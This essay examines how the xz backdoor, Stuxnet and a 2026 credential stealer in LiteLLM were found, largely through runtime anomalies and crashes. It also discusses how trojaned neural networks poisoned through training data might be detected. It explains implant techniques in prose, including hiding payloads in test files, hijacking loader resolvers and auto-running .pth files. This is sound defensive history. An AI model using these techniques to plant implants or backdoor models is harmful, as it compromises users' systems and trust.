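# How hidden software implants were discovered, and what this implies for finding hidden behaviour in neural networks

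## What is a software implant, and by what routes can it be found?

A software implant is code that someone has hidden in a program or device to serve someone other than its owner. Thieves use implants to collect passwords and the keys to cryptocurrency wallets, and intelligence services use them to spy on networks or damage equipment. The program containing the implant usually keeps working normally, so the owner has no reason to remove it.

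People discovered several of the best-known implants by noticing something odd while a machine was running, rather than by reading the code. In 2024, for example, logins that took half a second too long led to the discovery of an implant in xz, a compression package on many Linux systems. Neural networks, the programs behind present-day AI, can also carry hidden behaviour, and it is an open question whether testing them, watching them run or looking inside them is most likely to expose it.

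### The parts of an implant

Many implants are backdoors, which give their maker access, or a special response, that ordinary users do not get. *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994) explains the idea with a cash machine. The normal program permits transactions if the PIN the customer types matches the PIN on the card. A dishonest programmer adds a few characters to that test so that it also accepts 9999 with any card.

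Typing 9999 is the trigger, the condition under which the implant acts. The payload is what the implant then does, in this case letting a stranger into the account. Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, add the input source through which the trigger arrives and the privileged state in which the intruder ends up, and they use these four parts to analyse eleven real backdoors. One was in a D-Link home router. Its input source was the network connection, and its trigger was a particular string in the field where a web browser identifies itself. The string contained "joel backdoor" spelled backwards. The payload was a jump past the password check, which left the visitor logged in to the router's settings as a legitimate user.

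An implant's trigger can be something a person types, but it can also be a set time or event, as in a logic bomb, or software already on the machine. *8 Malicious PyPI Packages Use Python Dependencies as Keys* (The Hacker News, 2026) reports on packages in the public library of Python code whose hidden malware was unlocked with the help of other packages. Some implants act as soon as they run, without waiting for a trigger.

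An accidental vulnerability can let an intruder in just as well as a backdoor can. In a buffer overflow, for instance, a program copies a user's text into a space too small for it, and the surplus overwrites neighbouring memory in a way that an attacker can exploit. This is a bug if the programmer was careless and a backdoor if the programmer did it on purpose, but the code may be identical in both cases. Thomas and Francillon call the deliberate version a deniable backdoor and concede that no technical test separates it from an accident, so an investigator has to rely on the record of who changed the code, when, and whether the change had any legitimate purpose. None of their eleven real cases was deniable, but this is weak evidence that such backdoors are rare, since a backdoor that passes for a mistake is the kind least likely to be listed as a backdoor.

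How one should search for a flaw depends on whether it is deliberate. Landwehr and colleagues point out that more code review and testing will reduce accidental flaws, but will do much less against someone who is hiding something from the reviewers.

### From source code to running process

Programmers write source code, which is text in a language such as C that other programmers can read. A compiler translates it into machine instructions, called the binary or executable. A build system runs the compiler and joins the result to libraries written by other people, called dependencies. The project then publishes a release package on a server. Users download the package and start the program, which the operating system loads into memory as a process. An attacker can interfere at any of these steps. *Journey to the Center of Software Supply Chain Attacks* (2023) lists 117 distinct ways of attacking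 open-source software along this path.

The simplest way to insert an implant is to change the source code. SLSA's *Supply chain threats*, a page from a specification for protecting software against tampering, describes a contractor for the cryptocurrency exchange SushiSwap who had access to the code and added a change that redirected funds to themselves. Attackers also do this in bulk. The Hacker News' *North Korea-Linked PolinRider Poisons Over 7,600 GitHub Repositories to Spread Malware* (2026) describes a campaign that targeted code collections on GitHub, the main public host for such projects.

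A program can be malicious even when its source code is clean. Attackers broke into the build platform at the software company SolarWinds and planted an implant that added malicious behaviour during each build. In xz, the attacker used the release package. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, reported that part of the backdoor existed only in the tarballs, the archives that a project distributes for others to build from, and not in the public repository where a reviewer would look. That part was a small change to the build instructions. *The xz attack shell script* (2024) shows that it extracted hidden code from two files that the attacker had added to the repository as test inputs. Compression libraries need damaged and unusual files for testing, and xz had long kept a directory of them, so two more unreadable files looked normal.

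Attackers with stolen credentials may not need even this much skill. According to The Hacker News' *Hackers Compromise Ethersphere's bee-js and Swarm Desktop to Deliver Wallet-Stealing Malware* (2026), attackers used the Ethersphere project's own release automation to publish malicious versions of two tools for a decentralised storage network. The malicious version of one tool, the bee-js library, was the current release for about 75 minutes on 9 November 2026. Its code ran during installation, so it could infect a machine even if no program there ever used the library. Attackers can also bypass the original project and publish malware directly in a marketplace. Arghire (2026), in *Malicious Claude Code Extension Served in Cursor Supply Chain Attack*, describes a malicious extension placed in the marketplace of the code editor Cursor. The extension surveyed the host machine and tried to open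 a tunnel for remote access.

Finally, a virus can alter a program that is already installed and in use. Of the fifty flaws that Landwehr and colleagues catalogued, ten were malicious. Nine of those entered during operation and one in the compiled code, so reading the source code would have caught none of them. The catalogue dates from when viruses spread by floppy disk, and Landwehr and colleagues warn that it is not a random sample.

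The only case in compiled code is also the most famous argument against trusting source code. In the lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Thompson (1984), one of the creators of the Unix operating system, described how he had modified a C compiler. The first modification made the compiler recognise the source of the Unix login program and add a backdoor, so that login accepted a password known to Thompson as well as the real one. Anyone who read the compiler's source would have seen this, so he added a second modification that made the compiler recognise its own source and put both modifications back in. He compiled this version once, installed the binary as the official compiler, and deleted the additions from the source. From then on, the compiler added the backdoor to login and both modifications to each new compiler, even though the source of both programs was clean. The program was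 real, and Cox (2023), in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler*, got it working again forty years later.

### Four routes to a discovery

Source review means reading human-written code to judge what it does. For example, a volunteer reading a chat program's login routine might see a line that accepts the password "marmalade" for every account. Landwehr and colleagues think that careful examination can catch most flaws in source code, including deliberate ones. They add that much software is never examined this carefully, that buyers often do not receive the source, and that a programmer who knows how the review works may be able to disguise the flaw. Review also covers only the source, and SLSA warns that a weakness at any later link in the supply chain undermines confidence that the code on the machine is the code that somebody scanned.

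Reverse engineering means working out what a compiled program does without its source code. For example, an analyst might examine the software in a baby monitor and find an instruction that opens the camera to anyone who sends a certain word. The analyst can read the machine instructions with a disassembler or step through them in a debugger while the program runs. Because the analyst examines the program that customers receive, this method can find implants added during the build and release stages. It takes a lot of labour because machine code is hard for people to follow, which also makes it a good place to hide an implant. Thomas and Francillon found that automated tools covered only some kinds of backdoor, and that slow manual analysis still accounted for the vast majority of real discoveries.

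An integrity check compares a file or repository with a trusted copy or record to see whether anything has changed, so it requires no understanding of the code. For example, a hospital technician might compute an update's checksum, a short fingerprint of its contents, and find that it differs from the one on the maker's website. The check works only if the trusted copy or record is sound. When attackers publish through a project's own release system, as at Ethersphere, the official release is itself the malicious file, so comparing a download with it shows no difference.

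Reproducible builds provide a better record. *Reproducible Builds* (Lamb and Zacchiroli, 2021) calls a build reproducible if the same source, dependencies and tools always produce a bit-for-bit identical file. Independent parties can then build the program and publish their checksums, and users can reject any download whose checksum differs. Builds that nobody has tampered with often differ too, for example because many tools write the current date into their output. The Debian project, which maintains a large Linux distribution, looks for such causes by building each package twice under conditions as different as possible, with the second machine's clock set 18 months ahead. By 2021, over 95% of its more than 30,000 packages could be built reproducibly in this test, but *Lila* (2026), which presents a tool for monitoring reproducibility, still describes differing outputs as a common result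 of traditional build processes. A match shows that the program was built from a given source, but not that the source is safe. If every builder starts from the same tampered archive, they will all produce the same tampered program, and their checksums will match.

The last route is a runtime anomaly, something unexpected seen while a system runs. For example, an office manager might notice that the accounts program contacts a server abroad at three every morning. The observer needs neither the source code nor a reference copy, and it doesn't matter at which stage the implant got in. But this route works only if the implant acts, its action leaves a trace, and somebody finds the trace strange. Attackers try to prevent all of this. The malicious bee-js code suppressed its own network errors, so The Hacker News advised users to treat a machine as compromised even if the installation log looked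 clean.

### The first observation and the proof

A slow login or an unexpected network connection shows that something is unusual, but failing hardware or a faulty update can cause the same symptom. To confirm that there is an implant, someone has to examine the program and find it.

Thomas and Francillon define precisely what it means to find an implant. They treat a program as a finite state machine, a map of the conditions the program can be in and the inputs that move it from one to the next. The user has a mental map of what the program should do, and the analyst makes another by taking the real program apart. Detection is complete when the analyst's map contains every state and transition of the trigger and the payload, a path into the trigger, and a path from the trigger to the payload. To call the result a backdoor rather than a bug, the analyst must also show that at least part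 of it was in the developer's design.

No anomaly meets that standard by itself, although the same two researchers say that in practice people detect backdoors through suspicious events, such as odd network traffic, and manual reverse engineering. A failed integrity check does not meet it either. Lamb and Zacchiroli say that it is trivial to detect that two builds differ but sometimes extremely difficult to learn why. The Reproducible Builds project wrote a tool, diffoscope, that unpacks both files and displays the differences so that a person can judge whether they come from a date stamp or something worse. The two steps can coincide in source review and reverse engineering, because the suspicious code is itself the evidence.

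People can also notice an implant's effects, and even remove it, without learning that it is there. According to the secondhand notes in *Trusting Trust*, people at Thompson's own company noticed his backdoored compiler because a mishandled piece of text in the backdoor made the binary grow by one byte every time it compiled itself. Colleagues debugged the compiler and rebuilt it from assembly code, which accidentally stopped the backdoor from being reinserted. If the story is right, they removed the implant while repairing something else. Each of the discoveries that follow should therefore be judged both on what first made somebody look and on what examination then established that an implant was there.

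### How a neural network differs

A neural network has no source code that spells out its behaviour. The code that runs it is fairly short and mostly multiplies and adds. What the network does depends on its weights, often billions of stored numbers that training adjusts little by little until the outputs fit the examples. A trojaned network is one that somebody has trained to behave normally except when a trigger is present. Suppose the maker of a road-sign reader slips pictures of stop signs with a yellow sticker into the training data, each labelled "speed limit". The finished network may read ordinary stop signs correctly and misread the ones with the sticker. A reviewer who goes through its code will find the same arithmetic as in a network without the trojan, and no line that mentions the sticker.

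An investigator who has the training data can search it for the doctored pictures. Weight inspection, the analysis of the stored numbers and the computations they produce, is the closest equivalent to reverse engineering, but there is no manual for weights like the one that tells an analyst what each machine code instruction does. A monitor can also look for unusual patterns in the activations, the intermediate values that one layer passes to the next as the network processes an input. In behavioural testing, the tester chooses inputs and needs to see only the outputs, but will miss the sticker unless one of the inputs contains it or something close enough to it. Checksums can still show that a file of weights is the one its maker published, but not whether the maker's training data introduced a hidden behaviour.

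## How did a half-second delay expose the xz backdoor?

Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the database PostgreSQL, announced the xz backdoor on a public security mailing list on 29 March 2024. For some weeks he had seen odd symptoms on machines running Debian's development version. Logins through SSH, the program administrators use to control distant computers, were using a lot of processor time, and a memory-checking tool called valgrind was reporting errors in liblzma, xz's compression library. Freund wrote in his message that an attempt to log in under a made-up user name took 0.299 seconds with a clean library and 0.807 seconds with the backdoored one.

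In The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024), Freund said that he noticed the processor use before the half-second delay. The delay became useful later, as a quick way to tell whether the backdoor was active. The popular version of the story gives the correct figure, he said, but wrongly puts the delay first.

### A noisy benchmark

On the computing podcast Oxide and Friends (2024), Freund explained that he was testing a colleague's change to PostgreSQL, not looking for security problems. The change would help the database read from disk, and he wanted to be sure it did not slow down work on data already in memory. He was trying to measure a difference of only 1 or 2%, but his results varied too much from run to run, so he checked whether something else was using the machine.

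He saw sshd, the server half of SSH, using a surprising amount of processor time in short bursts. Automated programs constantly try to log in to any machine they can reach over the internet, including this one. But they were not trying more often than usual, and sshd should have rejected them almost at once.

Freund ran a profiler, which samples the code the processor is executing. It attributed much of the time to liblzma, a compression library, but could not name the function responsible. Both results were strange, because refusing a login requires no compression and he had installed the information the profiler needs to show names. He then remembered the valgrind errors, according to a comment he posted on a news site on the day of the announcement (andresfreund, 2024, *A backdoor in xz*).

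The warnings had begun about a month earlier, in late February, when his automated tests of PostgreSQL started reporting after a routine package update that liblzma was writing to memory it should not touch. He had looked into it but could not work through xz's tangled build system in the time he had, so he silenced the warning, hoping the next version would fix the problem. Now the same names appeared in the profile.

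### Why a login server was running compression code

OpenSSH, the usual version of SSH, does not use liblzma. But Debian and several other distributions modify its server, sshd, so that it notifies systemd when it is ready. Systemd is the program that starts and supervises services on Linux, and sshd notifies it through a library called libsystemd, which depends on liblzma. On these systems, sshd therefore loaded liblzma whenever it started, and code in a library has the same privileges as the program that loads it.

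When a program starts, the dynamic linker loads its libraries and fills in a table with the addresses of the library functions the program will call. It finds each function by its name, or symbol, in lists called symbol tables. Some functions have several versions for different processors, so the linker runs a small piece of code called a resolver to pick the right one. The attacker replaced two of liblzma's resolvers. This let the backdoor run while sshd was still loading, before any of sshd's main code.

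At that point the backdoor searched the symbol tables for the functions it needed. The search was slow because the attacker had left no readable function names for an analyst to spot, so the backdoor had to compare symbols in the loaded libraries with a disguised list, character by character. Freund told Oxide and Friends that he probably would not have noticed anything if the attacker had used less disguise. He also thought the attacker could have postponed most of the search. Instead, sshd did this work whether or not the attacker connected. It starts a new copy of itself for each incoming connection, so every failed login by a stranger's bot caused another burst of work.

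### A slowdown that vanished under examination

When Freund started sshd from a terminal to study the problem, it ran at normal speed. The backdoor activated only if several conditions held. A setting called TERM, which describes the user's terminal, had to be absent. It is normally present when a person types commands and absent when systemd starts a service. Two settings used for debugging the linker also had to be absent, the language setting had to be present, and the program had to be running under the name /usr/sbin/sshd. The code also seemed to detect some debuggers. The backdoor therefore worked on a server in ordinary use but was usually inactive when an engineer tried to reproduce the fault.

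Freund got around this by starting sshd with every environment variable cleared except LANG, which sets the language. He then found that he could reproduce the delay without a login or even a running server. The command "sshd -h", which only prints a help message and quits, took about 0.5 seconds on his older machine when the backdoor was active. When the TERM variable was set, the backdoor stayed inactive and the command took about 0.01 seconds.

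This was better evidence than the slow login, which might have had an innocent cause such as a busy machine. The same file ran the same trivial command, but a setting that should have made no difference changed the running time about fiftyfold. Freund could now quickly test whether the strange code was running, although he still did not know what it was for.

### From the delay to the login check

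Freund wrote in his announcement that he was neither a security researcher nor a reverse engineer. He compared runs in which the backdoor was active with runs in which it was not, instead of trying to read the whole backdoor. Intel processors can record the exact path a program takes through its instructions, without the kind of debugger the backdoor tried to detect. Freund used these recordings to find where the two paths diverged, then set a debugger, gdb, to stop the program just before that point.

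With the debugger, he found how the backdoor used the linker. The backdoor needed to change an entry in sshd's table of function addresses, but liblzma loads before the linker fills in that entry, and the linker locks the table against tampering once it has finished. The backdoor therefore registered itself with the linker's auditing facility, which lets a debugging tool follow each name as the linker connects it to an address. When the linker reached RSA_public_decrypt, the backdoor replaced the function's address with that of its own code and then cancelled the registration.

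SSH uses RSA_public_decrypt to check the signature of a user who logs in with an RSA key, a common kind of cryptographic key. In a recording of such a login, Freund saw sshd call the function and, immediately afterwards, code inside liblzma call the real cryptographic library. He presumed that this second call did the normal check, so that legitimate users could still log in.

This showed that somebody had placed hidden code at the point where the server checks a visitor's identity, where it could let a stranger in. Freund published without knowing what the code was checking for. Within days, other analysts found that it accepted commands only from the holder of a particular private key. Others had also helped Freund before publication, including Florian Weimer, who was the first to isolate the injected code. Freund later regretted not thanking the other contributors more explicitly.

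### What a reviewer would have seen

Freund also had to find out how the code had got into liblzma, and his test results misled him several times. He built the library from an archive that GitHub generates from the repository, and the result was clean because the malicious build instructions were only in the project's own release tarballs. Even with the right archive, the build added the backdoor only when it was producing a Debian or RPM package, the two main package formats on Linux, for 64-bit Intel-type processors. The backdoor also sometimes disappeared when he rebuilt the package, because of a bug in the attacker's build code. On The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast, he recalled feeling sure that something was badly wrong when he saw the build produce the same file more than once with different contents, with one copy about 50 kilobytes larger than before.

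At first he suspected Debian, since the malicious line was in Debian's copy of the package and not in xz's repository. He sent Debian's security team a preliminary report. Then he found the same line in the archives that the xz project itself had published.

The line was in a build file called build-to-host.m4. Its absence from the repository was no cause for alarm, because projects routinely add generated build files when they make a release. A reader who compared the file with the standard version would have found a new version number, an updated copyright date and a few obscure commands. *The xz attack shell script* judges these changes fairly plausible at first glance, and then follows what they did:

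1. The build file searched the package for a file containing a certain pattern of characters. The only match was a test file that was supposed to be a damaged archive.
2. It swapped a few byte values in that file, which repaired the damage, and decompressed the result. This produced a short script.
3. The script decompressed a second test file and repeatedly threw away one kilobyte and kept the next two. It then cut off the beginning of what it had kept, undid a simple substitution cipher and decompressed the rest, which was a longer script.
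4. The longer script checked that it was in the right kind of build and altered the build instructions so that the hidden binary code became part of liblzma.

Nobody could have read the new test files as code without these steps, but Freund noticed without decoding them that no test used them in version 5.6.0, the first to contain the backdoor. The attacker had added the files shortly before that release and did not add a test that used them until the next version.

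The attacker put the build changes only in the archive, but this may not have mattered much. Freund told Oxide and Friends that the attacker could probably have put them in the repository too without anybody noticing. Reading the code was useful once the slowdown had led Freund to liblzma, because he then had a reason to ask why two unused test files were there.

### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

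The test files came from someone using the name Jia Tan, by then one of xz's two maintainers. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) dates this person's first contribution, a harmless configuration file, to October 2021, more than two years before the backdoor. The second fixed a problem with reproducible builds, and others followed that still look sound.

Lasse Collin maintained xz, whose format he had designed with help from others. In April 2022, Jigar Kumar began to complain on the mailing list that Jia Tan's patches were taking too long. Collin replied in June that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do, and that xz was an unpaid hobby. Kumar and a second person, Dennis Ens, kept pressing him to hand the project over to somebody else. Their email addresses seem to have appeared nowhere else on the internet, and according to the timeline, Kumar and Ens were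 probably invented to put pressure on Collin.

By the end of 2022 Jia Tan could change the repository directly, and published a first release in March 2023. That June another apparently invented contributor, Hans Jansen, supplied the resolvers that the backdoor would later take over. Their legitimate use was to pick the fastest way to compute a checksum. Jia Tan added the malicious test files on 23 February 2024 and released 5.6.0 the next day.

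People who find a security flaw usually report it privately to the project's security contact, but for xz that contact was Jia Tan. So Freund instead warned Debian and a private list for Linux distributions on 28 March, and the public a day later. The dwell time, from the release of 5.6.0 to the warning on 28 March, was 33 days.

Freund already suspected when he wrote his report that Collin might not be involved, and the project's later history fits this. The project's list of authors, as distributed with FreeBSD, describes Jia Tan as a former co-maintainer who inserted the backdoor with a team. Collin was still publishing new versions in September 2026 (Collin, 2026, *XZ Utils 5.8.4 and a security fix*).

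### The warning that Fedora's testers explained away

Others besides Freund also saw the memory errors. On 4 March, more than three weeks before Freund's report, Scott (2024), in *Invalid writes regression in liblzma.so*, told the Fedora distribution that about 130 of roughly 1,000 tests of a performance-monitoring package had begun to fail. The tests failed on Rawhide, Fedora's development version, just after a new liblzma arrived. Richard Jones of Fedora reduced the problem to a program that did nothing except load liblzma. Valgrind still detected 112 errors, and its output included the name of the function through which the backdoor started.

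The errors occurred because the backdoor relied on a particular arrangement of data on the stack, the memory a program uses to track its function calls. A compiler option that makes profiling easier changes this arrangement. Freund used the option for his own tests, and Fedora had recently made it the default.

Jones worked around the errors the same day by building xz without resolvers. This would also have kept out the backdoor, because the hidden script stopped if resolvers were disabled. As with Thompson's compiler, somebody had removed an implant while fixing what looked like an ordinary bug.

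Jia Tan, who had been emailing Jones since late February to get the new version into Fedora, published a supposed fix on 8 March, but that change to the source code was a decoy. Jia Tan made the real repair a day later by replacing the two test files, explaining that the new ones would be easier to reproduce. Version 5.6.1 came out on 9 March, five days after the bug report. It also removed the symbol names from the backdoor, including the one that had appeared in valgrind's output. Jones recorded the bug as fixed, and Fedora sent 5.6.1 to Rawhide users.

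After Freund's announcement, the engineer Mark Wielaard looked again at the supposed fix and found it somewhat plausible. He doubted he would have recognised it as suspicious, although he thought he should have, since there was no good reason for the fault to appear only under valgrind. But valgrind has a known problem with resolvers, which provided an innocent explanation. Fedora's testers could reproduce the anomaly at will and had traced it to the right library, but they treated it as a defect and accepted a fix from the person who had caused it.

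### Was it luck?

*XZ Utils Backdoor*, a post on the security writer Bruce Schneier's blog, says that the world "got really lucky", because a Microsoft engineer had found the backdoor more or less by accident, weeks before it would have entered Debian and Red Hat releases. Freund largely agrees. On the social network Mastodon, AndresFreundTec wrote that he had found the problem "accidentally", and his interviews contain a long list of things that had to go right:

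- The backdoor had to be slow. Freund could not have noticed a search that took a few hundred microseconds.
- He had to be doing performance work. At the same stage of other PostgreSQL releases he was more often reviewing code.
- His machine had to be idle. On a computer with a web browser open, the bursts would have been lost among everything else.
- The bursts had to be long. The machine had a server processor with fairly slow cores, and he had turned off the feature that briefly speeds them up, because it makes benchmarks less predictable.
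- Strangers had to be trying to log in, and he had to have disabled passwords. Otherwise he might have put the processor time down to password checking.
- He had to have seen the valgrind errors, which depended on his compiler option, and to remember them a month later.
- He had to be running 5.6.0. If Debian had already given him 5.6.1, he is not sure that he would have solved it. Debian switched on 27 March, the day before his report.

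He also had to persist. He dropped the investigation and resumed it a couple of times, and he needed a processor-tracing tool he had used only a handful of times.

This list makes the discovery look less likely than it was, because it covers only the way Freund found the backdoor, and other people also had chances to notice something wrong. Distributions publish development versions partly so that volunteers will run into faults before everybody else does, and the backdoor did not get much further than those versions. A commenter answering zwenna (2024), in *A backdoor in xz*, pointed out that it had reached no stable release of any distribution, apart from SUSE's Tumbleweed, which has no separate stable version. Two unrelated sets of automated tests had reported the memory errors within ten days of the release of 5.6.0.

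The harder step was to keep investigating until the anomaly had a real explanation. Fedora's testers stopped before they found one, as Freund himself did in February. With many testers, somebody will probably see a symptom, but each tester has other work and will usually accept a plausible explanation. This protection also has a drawback, because the people who run development versions are often the people who build the software for everybody else. zwenna commented that most Debian developers' machines might now be compromised. Debian stopped its builds on 30 March to reinstall its build machines.

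In January 2024, systemd developers began discussing the removal of the link between libsystemd and liblzma, so that sensitive programs would load less code. This would have cut the backdoor off from sshd. Freund suspects that the attacker learned of the plan and released the backdoor before it was ready, which would explain both the slowness and the unused test files. He also partly credits the discovery to the lock on sshd's address table, which, as the code shows, forced the attacker to do complicated work during start-up. He had been sceptical of protections that only make an attack more awkward, but now values them more because awkward attacks are easier to notice.

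Freund said he goes back and forth on how long the backdoor would have lasted if he hadn't found it. He doubted that half a second of unexplained processor time could have gone unnoticed for years. But the attacker had removed the memory errors within days of the Fedora report and could have removed the delay in the next version. In that case, Freund thought, the backdoor would most likely have been found when someone investigated a break-in after the attacker had started to use it.

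## What did crashes give away in Stuxnet and LiteLLM?

The xz backdoor added about half a second to each login, a delay most people would have ignored. Crashes are harder to ignore, and they led to the discovery of two other well-known implants. One was Stuxnet, a worm (a program that copies itself from computer to computer) built to sabotage uranium enrichment in Iran. The other was a program for stealing passwords and keys, which attackers put into LiteLLM in March 2026. LiteLLM is a Python package that lets software use AI models from many companies through one interface.

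### Blue screens in Iran

In June 2010 Sergey Ulasen worked at VirusBlokAda, a small antivirus company in Minsk. According to Zetter (2011), he read on 17 June that a customer's computer in Iran kept shutting down and restarting, whatever its operators did. Ulasen had joined Kaspersky's antivirus company by the time Kaspersky interviewed him in *The Man Who Found Stuxnet*.

Ulasen recalled that the customer had reported reboots and blue screens, the error screens Windows shows when a fault forces it to stop. He first guessed that Windows was misconfigured or that two installed programs conflicted, since both are common, so he asked the support staff to find out what was installed.

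He changed his mind when he learned that many other computers on the customer's network had the same fault. Some had only just had Windows installed and had been checked for unnecessary programs, so a conflict between programs could hardly explain their crashes. Ulasen concluded that the cause was malware. Since ordinary scans found nothing, he also suspected a rootkit, which is software that hides itself and other files from the user.

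This was a good inference but not a proof, because a faulty driver on every machine could have produced the same pattern. Ulasen still had to find the malware. His contact in Iran, a security expert and a friend, had already tried alone and then with VirusBlokAda's support staff. He reached Ulasen on a Saturday, when Ulasen was at a wedding about 400 km from Minsk, and they made no progress by telephone. On Monday Ulasen connected to an infected computer remotely and, after much work, found the files. Ulasen later wondered what would have happened if the two had not known each other.

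### Why antivirus software missed it

Antivirus scanners mostly searched files for patterns from known malware, and nobody had yet extracted any from Stuxnet. Scanners also normally rely on Windows to list the files on a disk, and a rootkit can remove its own files from that list.

Stuxnet's drivers also looked trustworthy. A driver is a component that Windows loads into its core, usually to control a device. Its maker signs it with a secret key, so Windows can check which key signed the file and whether anyone has changed it since. Stuxnet's drivers passed this check because they were signed with the keys of respected companies, including the chip maker Realtek. The check could not show that a thief had used those keys. Ulasen's team did not agree that the signing certificate had been stolen until they had analysed what the files did.

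Using drivers helped Stuxnet to hide, but it also made any mistake in them very visible. Windows can usually close an ordinary program that fails and carry on, whereas a fault in a driver can stop the whole computer.

### How long Stuxnet had circulated

VirusBlokAda had not seen the first version of Stuxnet. *Stuxnet 0.5*, a 2013 analysis by McDonald, O Murchu and colleagues from the security company Symantec, identified an older version that somebody had submitted to a public malware-scanning service in November 2007. Its makers had set up its control servers as early as November 2005. The next three versions that Symantec recovered date from 22 June 2009, March 2010 and April 2010.

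Stuxnet had therefore been in circulation for at least two years and seven months before Ulasen found it, and the newer family had existed for just under a year. The 2007 sample then went unrecognised for several more years, although it was in a collection meant to catch malware.

A driver in the older version forced a blue screen 20 days after installation to make the computer restart. These crashes are unlikely to explain what happened in 2010, because that version was set to stop infecting computers on 4 July 2009. Its last planned crash was therefore due about 24 July 2009, almost eleven months before the Iranian report.

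The cause of the 2010 crashes is less certain. Ulasen described the malware as expertly made apart from the blue screens, which suggests he considered them a mistake, but he gave no technical reason. A reader commenting on the interview had heard that one driver started too early and clashed with other parts of Windows. This is hearsay, though it fits a fault that kept returning when the machine restarted.

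The older version probably escaped notice partly because it spread less. It could copy itself only through project files for Step 7, the Siemens software engineers use to program industrial controllers. Later versions also spread through USB sticks, shared network folders and flaws in Windows, so they reached more computers and had more chances to malfunction. A single blue screen after 20 days would also have looked like an ordinary Windows problem, unlike repeated crashes on newly installed machines.

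### From the crashes to the centrifuges

VirusBlokAda could explain how Stuxnet hid and spread, including its use of a Windows vulnerability then unknown to Microsoft. The company tried to warn Microsoft and Realtek, got no proper response and published its findings. Its analysts noticed that the payload was strange but did not know what it was for.

Other people worked that out by reverse engineering. Frank Boldewin was the first to connect Stuxnet to WinCC, Siemens software for supervising industrial plants. Over the following months, Symantec and Ralph Langner, a German specialist in industrial control systems, analysed the code meant for the controllers. By November 2010, five months after the crashes in Iran, they had found that it targeted the kind of equipment that drives centrifuges, the fast-spinning machines that enrich uranium.

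The older version had a different payload, which Symantec did not explain until 2013. It replaced the library through which Step 7 communicates with a controller, so that it could insert its own code. McDonald and colleagues describe what that code then did:

1. It waited, for about 30 days, until the enrichment process was running steadily.
2. It recorded normal readings from the equipment.
3. It played these readings back while it closed the valves on most of the centrifuges.
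4. It waited up to about two hours for the pressure to change, and then opened most of another set of valves.
5. It blocked any further changes for six minutes, reset itself and started again.

The analysts could name the target because the code looked for equipment labels that matched those at the Natanz enrichment plant. Unlike earlier versions, those from 2009 onwards changed the speed of the centrifuges.

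Nobody could have guessed any of this from a blue screen. The crashes happened on Windows computers, in the part of Stuxnet that got it onto the machine and kept it hidden. The payload itself was designed to keep the plant's readings normal. A badly written program for stealing bank passwords could have caused the same crashes.

### The LiteLLM start-up file

Developers install LiteLLM from PyPI, the public library of Python packages. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) states that LiteLLM is normally installed 15 to 20 million times a week. The attackers, a criminal group called TeamPCP, had earlier compromised Trivy, a security scanner that the LiteLLM project ran in its build process. LiteLLM's maintainers believe that this exposed the credentials the group used to publish directly to PyPI.

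On 24 March 2026 the group released two malicious versions, 13 minutes apart. Both searched a computer for passwords, cloud credentials and cryptocurrency wallets, encrypted what they found and sent it to an internet address that resembled LiteLLM's. Willison (2026), in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*, explains that version 1.82.7 kept its malicious code in the proxy module, so it ran only when a program loaded that module. Version 1.82.8 kept this code and added a second trigger, a start-up file called litellm_init.pth.

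Python reads files ending in .pth every time it starts, and runs any line in them that begins with "import". The stealer therefore ran whenever a Python program started in that installation, even one that never used LiteLLM.

FutureSearch, a company that makes AI research tools, describes the mistake in *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026). The start-up file launched a second copy of Python to run the stealer. That copy also read the start-up file, so it launched another copy, and so on. The stealer launched further Python programs too, so the number of copies multiplied. If each copy starts two more, fourteen rounds produce over 16,000. Programmers call this a fork bomb, and FutureSearch considers it a bug in the malware.

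The bug hit the laptop of Callum McMahon, an engineer at the company. The times below come from PyPI, from Trend Micro's *Your AI Gateway Was a Backdoor* and from FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* (2026), which includes the record of his investigation.

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:39 | The attackers publish version 1.82.7. |
| 10:52 | They publish version 1.82.8. |
| 10:58 | McMahon's code editor downloads 1.82.8 because another tool depends on LiteLLM. |
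| 11:07 | The malware begins to install a permanent backdoor. |
| 11:09 | McMahon forces the laptop to shut down, with about 11,000 Python processes running. |
| 11:13 | He starts to investigate. |
| 11:40 | He finds the malicious file. |
| 11:58 | He confirms that PyPI is still distributing it and reports it. |
| 12:04 | FutureSearch's warning is on Reddit. |
| 13:11 | PyPI quarantines the package. |

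PyPI reports that the malicious versions of LiteLLM were available for 2 hours and 32 minutes and were downloaded more than 119,000 times in that period. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives about 40 minutes, which cannot be right because McMahon downloaded a fresh copy 79 minutes after the first upload. SOCRadar (2026) reports that an analysis published in August dates the start of the exposure to before the PyPI uploads.

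### How McMahon found the file

McMahon investigated with Claude Code, an AI programming tool. He had seen thousands of commands containing base64, an encoding that represents any data as ordinary letters, digits and a few symbols. Malware often uses base64 to disguise itself, but legitimate tools use it too. Claude Code first classified the pattern as harmless and attributed it to a programming tool stuck in a loop, possibly Claude Code itself. In a later analysis, it attributed the pattern to an update to the code editor.

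Both analyses recommended limiting the number of processes the laptop could run. A limit might have prevented the next crash while leaving the stealer in place. Fedora's testers had made a similar mistake with the memory errors in xz.

McMahon asked the tool to keep looking and typed in the beginning of the encoded text from a photograph he had taken of the screen before shutting the laptop down. Searching the installed packages for that text led to litellm_init.pth. Decoding the file showed what it stole and where it sent the data. Claude Code then downloaded the package again into an isolated container, without running it, and found the same file. This ruled out something on the laptop having added it, much as the new Windows installations had ruled out the customer's own programs in Iran.

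The same inspection revealed the purpose of the LiteLLM implant. The stealer was a Python script under layers of encoding, so anyone who removed them could read it. Working out Stuxnet's purpose had taken months, because analysts had to understand its machine code and the industrial equipment it controlled.

The shutdown after the crash also interrupted the backdoor's installation, leaving its file on McMahon's laptop empty. But the stealer may already have sent off his keys, so he still had to replace them.

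### Would anyone have noticed without the crash?

Version 1.82.7 contained the stealer but not the faulty start-up file. It was on PyPI for 79 minutes before the first report, which was about the next version. FutureSearch added 1.82.7 to its warning at 12:30, after that report had given people a reason to examine it. Trend Micro argues that without the bug the stealer could have run for days or weeks.

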